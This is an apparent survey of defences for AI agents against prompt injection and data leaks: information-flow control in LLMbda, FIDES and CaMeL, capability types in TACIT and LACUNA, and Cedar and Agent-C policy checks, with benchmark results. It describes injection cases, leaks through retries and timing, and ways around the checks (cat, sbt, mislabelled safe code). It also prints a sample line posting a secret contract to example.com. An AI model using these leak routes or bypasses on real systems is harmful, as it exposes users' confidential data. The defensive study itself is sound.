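Garby and colleagues wrote their proofs in Lean, a programming language that checks each step of a mathematical proof. They also used Lean to write the LLMbda interpreter, the program that calls the model, and proved that its outcomes have the probabilities given by the definitions in the security theorems. This proof assumes that the model's replies follow a fixed probability distribution for each conversation. To their knowledge, no earlier agent harness had machine-checked security theorems about its own executable.

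The proof does not cover the code that sends the network request to the model, the Python code that connects the interpreter to the benchmark, or the choice of policy. A developer still has to label each data source and put a check in front of each sensitive action. If the developer does both correctly and a plan contains no endorsement, even a fully compromised model cannot get past the checks.

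The protection depends heavily on the policy, as the banking tools that Garby and colleagues wrote for their tests show. The tool for sending money requires a trusted recipient, but according to their list, the tool for scheduling a payment requires only a trusted amount. An agent could therefore schedule a payment to an account number from an attacker's file, and the theorems would still hold. They describe their policies as a deliberate simplification for a proof of concept.

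### Stopping and timing

A program that stops or continues depending on a secret reveals up to one bit per run, which becomes serious if an attacker can restart it. Suppose the secret is a four-digit PIN and the attacker can make the program stop whenever the PIN is above a number they choose. Each run can halve the remaining possibilities, so 14 runs are enough to identify any of the 10,000 possible PINs.

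Garby and colleagues found a loop of this kind in CaMeL. When a plan fails, ordinary Python code outside the label-tracking interpreter starts another attempt with clean labels, even though the new attempt depends on the error from the last one. CaMeL censors the error messages to reduce the leak, but this carries no formal guarantee.

The agent Randori keeps its retry loop inside LLMbda, so an error caused by untrusted data would taint every later attempt. To avoid this, the model first tests its plan on an artificial bank account, where the file tool returns placeholder text and payments do nothing. The program touches real data only after the model has corrected its mistakes and written a final plan. An operator who automatically restarts the whole agent after a failure would still bring back the leak that the internal retry loop prevents.

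Response times can also leak information. If an agent makes an extra model call when the balance is high, anyone waiting for the reply can notice the delay. The LLMbda theorem compares final outcomes, not how long they take, and the formal model behind FIDES also leaves out timing and the length of network packets. A harness could release all replies after a fixed delay to hide these differences, but every request would then take as long as the slowest one.

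### FIDES and its weaker guarantee

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, by Costa and colleagues at Microsoft, describes FIDES, a system designed around a fixed planner, the part of the harness that decides whether to query the model, call a tool or finish. The planner keeps a label for the conversation and compares it with the label of each field in a tool's result. If a field would raise the conversation's label, the planner stores that field in a variable, hidden from the model. The model can then see an email's trusted fields but not its untrusted subject and body.

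If the model needs a hidden text, it can have a quarantined model process the text, or it can open the variable that holds it. Opening the variable adds the text's label to the conversation, which may rule out some later tool calls. Before each call, FIDES applies policies based on two rules. A consequential action must come from trusted data, and information may leave through a channel only if everyone who reads that channel is allowed to see it. Developers can relax the first rule for individual arguments, for instance by requiring a trusted recipient but allowing an untrusted message body.

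The formal guarantee is explicit secrecy, which is weaker than noninterference. Suppose the agent starts with stored data *d*₁ and takes a series of steps whose combined effect on the data is *g*. Explicit secrecy requires that, for any other data *d*₂ that looks the same to an observer, *g*(*d*₁) and *g*(*d*₂) also look the same. So repeating the same steps with different secrets would not change the visible result. The definition does not cover whether different secrets would lead the agent to take different steps. The program with `a` and `b` therefore satisfies it, because repeating "set `a` to false, send the email" gives the same visible result for any balance.

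Costa and colleagues deliberately accept this leak because full noninterference would essentially forbid an agent from calling any tool with public effects after calling one that may have read a secret. They judge that blocking direct flows is enough to stop most practical prompt injections. Garby and colleagues object that an agent can easily turn data into decisions, and that an attacker can make the resulting leaks efficient. The objection is strongest for agents that run model-written code, since a short loop can repeat a one-bit leak many times.

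FIDES also lets policies make exceptions for small types, such as yes-or-no answers, by adding the type to the label. Garby and colleagues complain that a reviewer looking at a run can't tell an intended exception from a leak. In LLMbda, the word `endorse` marks each exception in the program. But in Randori the model selects what to endorse, so a marked exception may not be justified.

### Tests on AgentDojo

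Both groups tested their agents on *AgentDojo* (2024), a benchmark with user tasks and 629 security test cases. Each test case pairs a legitimate task with an attack. According to *The Surface You Test Is Not the Surface That Breaks* (2026), the benchmark judges the attack by examining the agent's tool calls and the final state of the environment. The *AgentDojo* paper calls the benchmark's attacks relatively simple.

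With GPT-4o and no policy checks, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent and 21 against FIDES. With the checks switched on, none succeeded against either. These counts come from a manual review, which excluded some attacks that the benchmark had counted as successes even though the policy had blocked them or they broke no rule. Costa and colleagues labelled a field untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. This weakens the evidence from the zeros, because a real developer has to label the data without knowing where the attacks will appear.

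The checks make agents much less useful. In banking, the ordinary agent completed 98.8% of tasks without them and 37.5% with them. FIDES completed 52.5% with them, and across the four environments it averaged eight percentage points more than the ordinary agent under the same checks. Many of its banking failures were intentional. If a task requires the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, reading the file taints the conversation, and the policy then blocks the payment.

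Garby and colleagues tested Randori only on banking tasks. They paired each of 16 tasks with nine attacks and ran each pair three times on each of three models, for a total of 1,296 attacked runs. Randori resisted the attack in all but two. They also reran CaMeL on two of the models, with and without its policy checks, but some of the attacked CaMeL runs did not finish.

| Agent | Model | Tasks completed, no attack | Successful attacks |
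|---|---|---|---|
| Randori | GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | 2 of 432 |
| Randori | Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 0 of 432 |
| Randori | MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 0 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 62.5% | 0 of 432 |
| Randori without endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 54.2% | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL without policy checks | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
| CaMeL without policy checks | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 4 of 382 |
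| CaMeL with policy checks | GPT-5.2 | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL with policy checks | MiMo-v2.5 | 37.5% | 0 of 357 |

On this evidence, Randori completes about as many tasks as CaMeL does with its checks off, and roughly twice as many as CaMeL does with them on. But each percentage comes from only 16 tasks. Randori's completion rate on GPT-5.2 is 75%, with a 95% confidence interval of plus or minus 18.9 points, so the test could have missed a considerable difference from unchecked CaMeL. The comparison with checked CaMeL is also uneven, because Randori enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies and lets the model endorse data.

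The security figures provide little evidence about the labels. In 97 of the 144 pairs, the attack needs a tool call or file read that would never appear in a plan for the user's task, so writing the plan before reading untrusted data is generally enough to defeat it. Only the other 47 pairs test the labels, and on those CaMeL with GPT-5.2 resisted the attack in all 141 runs even without policy checks. The theorem is a better reason to trust LLMbda's labels than this benchmark, because too few of the benchmark's attacks could succeed without the labels.

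Both of Randori's failures involved the same task and the same attack, on GPT-5.2. The user asked the agent to read a text file and make the payment it described, which in effect gave payment authority to anyone who could edit the file. The attacker replaced the contents with a different payment request, and the agent endorsed the details from the file and paid. Garby and colleagues consider this outside the scope of information-flow control, because the agent would have to judge from the wording that the request was suspicious. They point out that Randori without endorsement blocks the attack but also cannot pay a genuine bill from a file. Restricting endorsement to a short list of values would not help with an account number the agent has never seen.

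## Permissions checked by a type system

LLMbda and FIDES compare labels while an agent is running. If the agent writes its actions as a program, a compiler can do a similar check before any of the code runs. The compiler works out which files, network connections and other resources each part of the program could use, and it rejects the program if any part exceeds its permissions. This works only if the permissions are visible in the code, as they are when the program represents them as capabilities. A capability is an unforgeable value that names a resource and grants permission to use it.

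### The confused deputy

In *The Confused Deputy*, Hardy (1988) tells a nearly true story about how he came to think capabilities were necessary. Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers, let customers run a compiler and choose a file for its debugging output. The compiler also recorded statistics in a file in a system directory, so Tymshare had given it permission to write to every file in that directory, including the billing records. One customer chose the billing file for the debugging output, and the compiler overwrote the records.

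The customer did not have permission to change the billing file, but the compiler did. Hardy calls the compiler a confused deputy because it acted with authority from two sources and could not keep them separate. It was supposed to use its own authority to write the statistics and the customer's to write the debugging output, but in both cases it gave the operating system only a file name.

The obvious repairs don't work well. A compiler that refused every file in the system directory would also block customers with legitimate access to it. A compiler that refused only the billing file would need an update whenever a new sensitive file appeared. Tymshare added a way for a program to choose between its own authority and the customer's, but some programs needed more than two. Meanwhile, the rule for when a program could open a file had grown to fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

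With capabilities, the customer passes the compiler a value that identifies the output file and carries permission to write to it. The compiler holds another capability for the statistics file. A customer who has no capability for the billing file cannot pass one to the compiler, even if they know the file's name.

An invoice agent can be a confused deputy too. It can move the company's money, which the supplier cannot do, and it may take the account number from the supplier's text. If the payment tool accepted only capabilities for approved payees, an injection could only direct money to one of those payees, as with the list of known billers.

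### How permissions spread

In the object-capability model, a program consists of objects that can affect one another only through the capabilities they hold. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) explains how this limits the spread of permissions. If Alice, Bob and Carol are objects, Alice can give Bob access to Carol only if Alice already holds capabilities for both. A transfer therefore can't connect two objects that had no path between them, and a developer can confine a program by never giving it a path to the outside.

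Alice can also make the access temporary. She creates a forwarder that relays messages to Carol, gives Bob the forwarder, and keeps the control that switches it off. When she switches it off, Bob and anyone he has passed the forwarder to lose access to Carol.

On Unix, as on most operating systems, a program that opens a file presents only the file's name, and the system decides whether the user may open it. Miller and colleagues call this ambient authority, because the program uses a permission without selecting it. A coding agent that runs shell commands under a user's account has ambient authority over everything that user can access.

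Some older systems represented capabilities as secret strings. This would be a poor choice for agents, because a language model that had read such a string could copy it into an email. If the model instead writes code that refers to a capability by a variable name, the name is useless outside the program.

### Capabilities recorded in types

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, a harness component that coding agents such as Claude Code can connect to. The agent sends TACIT short Scala 3 programs. TACIT compiles each one, runs it if it passes every check, and returns either the result or the compiler's errors. The programs can reach files, networks and other programs only through TACIT's library.

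The main check uses a Scala feature called capture checking, which gives each type a capture set listing every capability that a value of that type might use. If `f` is a capability for a file, a function that writes text to the file has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, which means that it takes a string, may use `f`, and returns no useful value. A function that converts text to capitals has the type `String -> String`. Its capture set is empty, so the function is pure, meaning that it can compute a result but cannot affect anything else.

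A value's capture set must include every capability the value uses, and it can include others. A value with a smaller set can go wherever the program permits a larger one. A pure function is therefore acceptable where the program permits one that may write to `f`, but not the other way around.

Odersky and colleagues list what the language must provide for the check to give a guarantee. Code must not be able to forge a capability or hide its need for one. Every effect that matters for safety must require a capability, unless the harness can contain that effect at run time. The compiler must be able to verify that a particular piece of code is pure, even if the rest of the program is not.

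### A container for secrets

When an agent reads a file from a folder marked as classified, TACIT returns the text in a container of type `Classified[String]`. The agent can't take the text out, but it can work on it through the container's `map` method, which applies a function to the contents and puts the result in a new container:

```
def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

Here `T` is the type of the contents and `U` is the type of the result. The plain arrow in `T -> U` means that `map` accepts only pure functions.

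Suppose an agent has permission to read a folder and to contact one web server, and submits this program:

```
val contract = readClassified("secret/contract.txt")
val summary = chat(contract.map(text => s"Summarize: $text"))
val sent = contract.map(text => httpPost("https://example.com", text))
```

1. On the first line, `contract` gets the type `Classified[String]`.
2. The function on the second line only puts a word in front of the text. It uses no capabilities, so its type is `String -> String` and the compiler accepts it. `chat` would then send the contents to a separate, trusted model and return the summary in another container.
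3. The function on the third line calls `httpPost`, which needs the network capability, here called `net`. Its type is `String ->{net} String`, but `map` requires an empty capture set, so the compiler reports an error.
4. TACIT runs none of the three lines. The agent receives the error and can submit the first two lines again without the third.

The agent had permission to use the network and permission to process the contract, but the compiler stopped it from combining them. In a recorded run, the compiler also rejected an agent's attempt to print a GitHub key inside `map`, because printing, like network access, needs a capability.

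The rule also prevents the leak through a branch that does not run. An agent might try to record whether a secret balance exceeds €1 million by changing an ordinary variable:

```
balance.map(b => if b > 1000000 then rich = true)
```

The compiler also tracks changes to variables outside a function, so it rejects this program whatever the balance is.

A function could divide by zero only when a secret has a certain value, and the compiler cannot rule this out, so TACIT catches such errors at run time and keeps the details from the agent.

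### Permissions that end with a block

An agent gets access to ordinary files by calling `requestFileSystem` with the name of a folder and a block of code. The library creates a capability, passes it to the block, and makes it invalid when the block ends. The agent might try to keep the permission by returning a function that uses it later:

```
val later = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("report.txt").read()
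}
```

The capture set of the returned function contains `fs`, which exists only inside the block. No type outside the block can refer to `fs`, so the compiler rejects the program. Putting the function in a list or an outer variable fails for the same reason. One agent in the tests made this mistake when it tried to return a list of open file handles.

Some checks can happen only while the program runs. A program may compute a file's path during execution, so the library tests each path and refuses any outside the requested folder. Network and command permissions work similarly, with lists of allowed web hosts and commands.

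In the published interface, the agent's code requests a folder, hosts and commands. The block then limits how long the permission lasts and where it can go. An operator who wants to limit what the agent can request has to build that limit into the library. The protection for classified text doesn't depend on such a limit, because `map` rejects the network call whichever hosts the agent requested.

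### Safe mode and separate outputs

Ordinary Scala has features that would let a program evade capture checking. A cast can make the compiler treat a value as having a different type, and reflection lets a program find and call functions by name while it runs. TACIT compiles all agent code in safe mode, which forbids both.

Safe mode also lets an agent call library code only if that code compiles in safe mode or a developer has marked it `@assumeSafe`. A developer might mark a cache that stores the results of a pure function in an untracked variable, because callers get the same answers with or without the cache. Scala's documentation gives the example of an email function that asks the user for confirmation before sending anything. Agents can call this function but not the unrestricted mailer it uses. As VirtusLab's *Safe Scala* points out, an agent cannot use the mark in its own code, because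 otherwise it could exempt that code from the checks.

The user may still need to read a confidential summary that the agent's model must not see. TACIT therefore sends printed output to both the user's terminal and the model. Both receive the same text unless the value is classified, in which case the terminal shows the contents and the model receives only `Classified(****)`.

If the user then asks how long the summary is, the agent can run `summary.map(_.length)` and print the answer. The user sees a number, while the model again receives asterisks. The permission to read the folder has expired by then, but the container is still available and still protects its contents. TACIT does not need to put a secrecy label on the conversation, because the secret never enters it. The drawback, as in the dual-LLM pattern, is that the agent's model can't base its next step on text it has not received.

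### The leakage test

Odersky and colleagues tested the container on a small software project with a folder of API keys, a database and confidential documents. They paired each of 12 legitimate tasks, such as summarising a classified incident report, with ten prompt injections. Some injections were plain instructions in code comments, while others imitated system errors or supplied ready-made code to read the secret files. In 11 further trials, the user was the attacker. The user asked for secrets outright in five of these trials and used a pretext in the other six, such as an administrator urgently needing to replace passwords.

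Each model had 131 trials in each mode. TACIT returned secrets in the container in one mode and as ordinary text in the other. A trial counted as secure if no secret appeared in the agent's output.

| Model | Trials | Leaks with the container | Leaks without it |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with injections | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 11 malicious requests | 0 | 2 |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with injections | 0 | 3 |
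| MiniMax M2.5 | 11 malicious requests | 0 | 8 |

With the container, every trial was secure. Without it, 98.5% of the trials with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and 91.6% of those with MiniMax M2.5 were secure.

The zero counts are modest evidence on their own. If the trials were independent, no leaks in 131 trials would be compatible with a true leak rate of up to about 2.3%, at 95% confidence. The same tasks and attacks recur, so the real uncertainty is larger, and the figure applies only to attacks like these. Claude also resisted all 120 injections without the container, so those trials could not show any benefit from it.

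The argument from types is much broader than the test because it covers every program an agent could submit. But it assumes that the compiler and library work as designed, and the test is most useful for checking that assumption. For instance, if a developer had forgotten to make the print function require a capability, one of the attacks might well have exposed the mistake. A few hundred trials are unlikely to find subtler mistakes.

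The tests also measured whether agents can still do their work, which the type argument cannot show. With the container, Claude completed 99.2% of the 120 trials with legitimate tasks and MiniMax completed 90.0%. Without it, Claude completed 83.3% and MiniMax 88.3%. Odersky and colleagues suggest that their setup lowered Claude's score in the unprotected mode, because Claude often ran out of turns or time and sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection. Hiding data probably did not make Claude more capable.

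### AgentDojo and ordinary work

The same researchers adapted the AgentDojo benchmark to TACIT and ran it with Gemini 2.5 Pro and o4-mini-high. Of 1,926 injection attempts, the benchmark counted one as successful. The user had asked to book one hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for another in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and the benchmark found the second hotel's name in the reply. This looks more like a scoring error than a failure of TACIT, since the policy allowed users to see reviews.

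Odersky and colleagues report that TACIT completes tasks at a rate comparable to that of CaMeL, the label-tracking agent. This overstates TACIT's results with o4-mini-high, which did worse with TACIT than with CaMeL in all four environments. In the office environment, it completed 52.9% of tasks with TACIT and 81.4% with CaMeL. With Gemini, TACIT was ahead in banking and travel and behind in the other two environments.

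It is also unclear how far this benchmark tested the rule about pure functions. Most of the tools that read emails, files and reviews returned containers, so much of the injected text never reached the agent's model. But the agent's instructions mentioned side effects inside functions passed to `map`, and the listed signature of the payment tool does not require a capability. The adapted version may therefore have allowed side effects in those functions, unlike the leakage test.

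Odersky and colleagues used two other benchmarks to test whether writing Scala instead of ordinary tool calls lowers performance. τ²-bench simulates customer service, and SWE-bench Lite consists of 300 real software bugs.

| Benchmark | Model | Ordinary tool calls | Scala with TACIT |
|---|---|---|---|
| τ²-bench, airline | gpt-oss-120b | 43.8% | 45.2% |
| τ²-bench, airline | MiniMax M2.5 | 58.4% | 61.0% |
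| τ²-bench, airline | DeepSeek V3.2 | 57.8% | 58.6% |
| τ²-bench, retail | gpt-oss-120b | 53.3% | 57.0% |
| τ²-bench, retail | MiniMax M2.5 | 75.1% | 77.5% |
| τ²-bench, retail | DeepSeek V3.2 | 74.6% | 75.5% |
| SWE-bench Lite | MiniMax M2.5 | 43.3% | 41.7% |

All six customer-service results, averaged over ten runs per task, slightly favour Scala. The researchers attribute this to the structured results that the Scala tools return and to the compiler's error messages. On SWE-bench Lite, the agent fixed five fewer faults with TACIT. On τ²-bench, only 0.3% to 7.9% of the models' Scala programs needed another attempt, and compilation usually took less than a second.

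So agents lose little performance on these tasks when they must write typed code. However, the customer-service tools returned their data as ordinary values, so these results do not show how much performance an agent loses when it cannot read the data it works on.

### LACUNA and typed holes

Several of the same researchers later built a variant in which the program itself calls the model for code. In *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026), the call `agent[T](task)` specifies a plain-language instruction, `task`, and the required result type, `T`. The call is a typed hole, a gap in a program that only code of a certain type can fill. When the program reaches the hole, the model writes the missing code. The compiler checks that code as if a programmer had written it there, and sends any errors back to the model for another attempt.

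One example starts with a balance of 100 and asks for an `Int`, a whole number:

```
var balance: Int = 100
agent[Int]("subtract 50 and return the new balance")
```

Suppose the model writes one line that subtracts 50 and another that returns the text "remaining: 50". The text is not a whole number, so the compiler rejects both lines and the balance stays at 100. A harness that ran the code line by line would subtract 50 before reaching the error, and a second attempt might subtract 50 again.

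This protection covers only mistakes that the compiler can find. If a program passes the check, subtracts 50 and then fails because a server is down, the 50 stays subtracted.

The generated code can use only the variables, functions and capabilities available at the hole, so a developer can give the model a network capability at one point in a program and withhold it at another. The code may also contain further `agent` calls, each with its own type. The compiler cannot determine whether a chain of these calls will end, so the runtime lets the developer limit its depth.

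LACUNA also makes the container more flexible. In TACIT, the agent has to write the function for `map` before anyone has looked at the contents. With LACUNA, that function can call a trusted local model, which reads the contract and writes code suited to it. The compiler checks the new code inside the same pure function, so that code cannot send the contract anywhere either.

LACUNA's performance results are weaker than TACIT's. On 392 customer-service tasks, DeepSeek V4 Flash solved 76.0% with LACUNA and 90.0% with ordinary tool calls. This 14-percentage-point gap is substantial, although Zhao and colleagues call the results "on par". With the weaker Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, the figures were 29.1% and 33.2%. That model often couldn't write valid Scala, and the compiler rejected 89% of its code in the telecom tasks. LACUNA also answered 27.1% of the hard search questions in BrowseComp-Plus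 with its best model, but without a tool-calling agent for comparison, this result doesn't show how much the type checks reduce performance.

On AgentDojo, eight of 1,898 injections succeeded against LACUNA, seven of them with Gemini 2.5 Pro. Zhao and colleagues point out that the compiler does not stop an attacker from steering the model into misusing a capability that the task needs.

### The trusted base

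TACIT's trusted base includes the Scala compiler, TACIT's own library, the software that runs the compiled code, and the second model if the agent uses one. The reusable part of the library is about 1,000 lines, short enough to review carefully. The compiler is far larger and would not meet Anderson's requirement that the mechanism be small enough to analyse completely.

Scala's documentation describes capture checking as "still highly experimental and unstable". The type system it builds on has machine-checked proofs, but Odersky and colleagues say a further argument is needed to show that safe mode provides the guarantees claimed for it. The evidence is therefore less complete than for LLMbda, whose designers proved their security theorems about the interpreter they actually run.

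A developer can also break the guarantee by wrongly marking a function `@assumeSafe`. If the function sends data over the network without declaring a capability, the compiler treats it as pure, and an agent can call it inside `map`.

External commands are a larger gap, because the compiler cannot check a program that Scala starts. An agent with permission to run `cat`, which prints files, could read a secret file and receive its contents as ordinary text. TACIT has a strict mode that blocks such file commands. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific safe commands, such as `sbt`, which builds Scala projects. But `sbt` runs code from the project's build files, so an agent that can edit those files could use it to run code that TACIT has never checked. The researchers advise adding a sandbox for security-critical uses.

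The second model must retain nothing between requests. `chat` needs no capability, so an agent can call it inside `map` and send the model a secret. If the model's service kept a history, the agent could then retrieve the secret as plain text by querying the model outside the container. The types cannot prevent this, so whoever runs the service has to ensure that it keeps no history and gives the model no tools. Timing can still leak information a bit at a time, and a user who pastes a classified summary into the chat passes it directly to the untrusted model.

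## Rules checked at each tool call

TACIT can check a whole program before it runs, but many agents make one tool call at a time and choose the next after seeing the result. For these agents, the harness can check each call against a policy, a machine-readable rule for which tool calls are allowed in which circumstances.

### From request to decision

Suppose a shop's support agent requests `refund(order: 88, amount: 60)`.

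1. The harness parses the request. It rejects an unknown function, a missing argument or an amount that is not a number.
2. The harness looks up the facts that the rules depend on. It takes the agent's identity from its login, the order's price and owner from the shop's database, and the earlier calls from a log that the agent cannot write to. The model supplies none of these, because a manipulated model could claim that the order cost €6,000.
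3. A policy engine evaluates the rules against the request and these facts. If the harness tracks labels, the rules can also cover where each argument came from.
4. The harness runs the tool, returns an error to the model, or holds the request until a person decides.

Cedar, a policy language developed at Amazon Web Services, keeps such rules separate from the application's code. Two Cedar rules for refunds could look like this:

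```
permit(
  principal == Agent::"support",
  action == Action::"refund",
  resource
) when {
  context.amount > 0 && context.amount <= resource.price
};

forbid(principal, action == Action::"refund", resource)
when { resource.refunded };
```

The principal is whoever makes the request, the resource is the order, and `context` holds other details such as the amount. Cedar allows a request if at least one `permit` rule matches and no `forbid` rule does, so it denies anything the rules do not mention. Together the two rules express the limits Brooker wanted, a refund of at most the original price and at most one refund per order. The rules work only if the shop marks the order as refunded in the same step as it pays, which the database has to ensure.

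Cedar skips any rule that causes an error when evaluated. This is safe for a `permit` rule, because skipping it can only lead to a refusal. But if the developer misspells `refunded` in the `forbid` rule, Cedar skips the ban and the agent can refund the same order repeatedly. A separate validator catches such mistakes in advance by checking the rules against a schema of the application's data, so developers should always run it.

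### Proofs about Cedar

Disselkoen, Eline and colleagues (2024), in *How We Built Cedar*, describe how they checked the language. They wrote a simple version of it in Lean, the language Garby and colleagues used for LLMbda, and proved seven properties:

- if any `forbid` rule matches, Cedar denies the request
- if no `permit` rule matches, Cedar denies the request
- if Cedar allows a request, some `permit` rule matched
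- the order of the rules and any duplicates make no difference
- when Cedar speeds up a decision by evaluating only the relevant rules, the decision is the same as with all of them
- a rule that the validator accepts never causes a type error
- every Cedar function finishes

These proofs cover the Lean model, but applications run a separate version written in Rust. The model has about 1,700 lines and the Rust code about 15,700, including a parser that the model leaves out. To check that the two versions agree, the team generates millions of random policies and requests, runs them through both and investigates any differences. Each test runs for six hours a day.

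Attempting the proofs exposed four bugs in the validator, and random testing exposed 21 more in various components. The tests also missed at least nine. In one, the Rust code wrongly implemented `in`, the operator that tests whether, for example, a user belongs to a group. Such a mistake could allow a forbidden request even though every theorem about the model is true. The team has fixed all these bugs, but it still relies on testing to check that the Rust code matches the model, unlike in LLMbda. Disselkoen and colleagues chose Rust because it is easier to maintain and debug, and because few developers know Lean.

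Cedar can also translate a set of rules into a logical formula for an SMT solver, a program that determines whether logical and arithmetic conditions can all be true at once. A developer who has reorganised the rules can use the solver to search for a request that the old rules allow and the new ones deny, or the reverse. If none exists, the two sets grant the same permissions. According to *Cedar* (2024), which introduced the language, its designers limited what rules can express partly to make this analysis exact.

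### A rule about order

"Refund only after verifying the customer's identity" depends on earlier calls as well as the current one. The harness can enforce it with a small state machine:

```
 +--------------+   verification succeeds   +--------------+
 | NOT VERIFIED | ------------------------> |   VERIFIED   |
 +--------------+                           +--------------+
   refund: refuse                             refund: allow
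   other calls: allow, stay here              other calls: allow, stay here
```

The harness starts each conversation in the left-hand state and moves it to the right-hand state only when the verification tool returns success. Failed attempts and model-written claims that the customer has been checked do not change the state.

This machine doesn't record whom the agent verified, so a customer who proves that she is Ana could then get a refund on Ben's order. The harness should store the verified customer's identity and allow a refund only if that customer owns the order. It should also return to the left-hand state when someone else takes over the conversation.

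In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider called such machines security automata. His first example bans sending messages after reading a file and also needs only two states. He warned that the ban works only if "send" covers every way to send a message, including those "buried deep within the bowels of the target". The refund rule has the same weakness if the agent can also issue store credit through another tool.

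### What a monitor cannot enforce

Schneider also determined which rules a monitor can enforce if it can only watch a program's steps and stop it before a forbidden one. He derived three conditions from these limits.

First, the monitor observes only one run, so the rule must be checkable on a single run. Noninterference isn't, because it compares runs. A runtime monitor can still prevent leaks by enforcing a stricter rule that also stops some harmless runs, as LLMbda does.

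The monitor also has only the steps so far to go on. If they break the rule, it must stop the program even if a later step would have repaired the damage, because the program might end before that step. So once a run has broken the rule, no later step may make it acceptable again. The monitor also has to act at some definite point, so every forbidden run must break the rule after a finite number of steps.

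Rules that meet these conditions are called safety properties. In symbols, let *σ* be a run, *σ*[..*i*] its first *i* steps, and *G* the set of acceptable runs. *G* is a safety property if

*σ* ∉ *G* ⟹ there is an *i* such that, for every continuation *τ*, *σ*[..*i*]*τ* ∉ *G*

For this class of rules, every unacceptable run has a beginning that no later call can make acceptable. The refund rule belongs to this class because once the agent has refunded an unverified customer, no later call can put a verification before the refund. More generally, Basin et al. (2012) place history-based access rules in this class.

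A monitor that can only stop the agent cannot enforce the rule "every complaint is eventually answered." However long a complaint has waited, the agent could still answer it next, so no finite history breaks the rule and the monitor never has a reason to intervene. Stopping the agent would also leave the complaint permanently unanswered.

Adding a deadline turns the requirement into a safety property, but a monitor still can't enforce it. Once a complaint has gone unanswered for more than 24 hours, the rule "answer every complaint within 24 hours" is irreversibly broken, and the monitor can't prevent this by stopping the agent, because time keeps passing. Schneider used a similar time limit to show that some safety properties are unenforceable. If the shop counts tool calls instead of hours, the monitor can enforce "make no more than ten other calls before answering", but the agent can comply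 by making no calls at all. In Schneider's own example, a seller who has received payment may do nothing except provide the service. A monitor can enforce this rule, but the seller can still keep the money and stop work.

An agent's harness usually returns an error instead of ending the run, so the model can try something else. Schneider found that this variation does not make any more rules enforceable. A harness that acts by itself, for instance by assigning every day-old complaint to an employee, goes beyond his definition of a monitor. It can ensure that the complaint is assigned, but not that the employee replies.

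### Agent-C

Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, built Agent-C, which lets developers write rules about the order of tool calls without drawing the state machine. Its main constructs are:

- `Before(A, …, B, …)`: any call to A needs an earlier call to B
- `After(A, …, B, …)`: any call to A needs a later call to B
- `Seq(A, …, B, …)`: the run must contain a call to A followed by a call to B
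- `Forall(A, …)`: every call to A must meet a condition

The dots stand for conditions on the arguments, on the results of earlier calls, and on the tools' stored data. For example, one rule lets the agent open an order's details only after it has looked up a customer by email. The lookup must have succeeded, the order must exist, and it must belong to that customer. These conditions close the hole in the two-state machine, but they don't prove that the person writing is that customer, since somebody else may know the email address.

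When the model proposes a call, Agent-C adds it to the history and gives the history and the rules to an SMT solver, which checks whether any continuation could satisfy all the rules. If the agent tries to open an order without a prior lookup, no continuation can satisfy them, because later calls can't change the history, so Agent-C discards the call. If the agent opens a file under the rule that it must later close it, a continuation that closes the file can satisfy the rules, so Agent-C allows the call.

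The file rule shows Schneider's limit in practice. If the model tries to finish with the file still open, Agent-C detects the violation and ends the run in an error state, but the file stays open.

After discarding a call, Agent-C makes the model try again. With an open-weight model, whose internal probabilities are accessible, it regenerates from the start of the tool call, but with a model behind a commercial interface it has to resend the whole prompt. If several attempts fail, Agent-C records an error message for the model and calls no real tool. It also refuses a call if the solver runs out of time, because it releases a call only after the solver returns a positive result.

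Kamath and colleagues prove that if the history satisfies the rules, it still satisfies them after Agent-C releases a call and that call is added. They assume that no other process changes the tools' data, which may not be true in a shop with several agents.

The evaluation of Agent-C used τ-bench, a benchmark of simulated customer service with 115 retail and 50 airline tasks. For comparison, the Qwen model was run with DynaGuard, in which a second language model judges each call, and with AgentSpec, another rule language. In the table, "obeyed" is the percentage of tasks in which the agent followed the policy, and "completed" is the percentage in which it both followed the policy and finished the task.

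| Model | Safeguard | Retail, obeyed | Retail, completed | Airline, obeyed | Airline, completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-32B | None | 37.7% | 25.5% | 35.3% | 17.3% |
| Qwen3-32B | DynaGuard | 77.1% | 9.6% | 69.4% | 17.0% |
| Qwen3-32B | AgentSpec | 84.1% | 37.4% | 79.3% | 38.7% |
| Qwen3-32B | Agent-C | 100% | 53.3% | 100% | 35.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | None | 93.0% | 76.5% | 70.0% | 42.0% |
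| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | Agent-C | 100% | 80.5% | 100% | 43.5% |
| GPT-5 | None | 91.9% | 71.0% | 71.3% | 38.0% |
| GPT-5 | Agent-C | 100% | 73.6% | 100% | 42.8% |

The 100% figures follow from the theorem, so they mainly show that the software works as designed. The completion rates are more informative, because a safeguard that refused everything would also score 100% on compliance. Agent-C raised completion for every model in the table, but part of the gain comes from the scoring, which gives an unprotected agent no credit for a finished task if it broke a rule along the way. Some differences are also tiny, such as Claude's gain of less than one task in 50 on the airline tasks.

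The researchers also wrote 17 malicious requests for each setting. In one, a customer who had paid by credit card insisted on a refund to a PayPal account. The prompt allowed refunds only to the original payment method or an existing gift card, but Claude without Agent-C attempted the PayPal refund. Claude carried out the harmful goal in five of the 17 retail attacks (29.4%) without Agent-C, and GPT-5 did so in 3.9% on average over three trials, while neither model did so in any of them with Agent-C.

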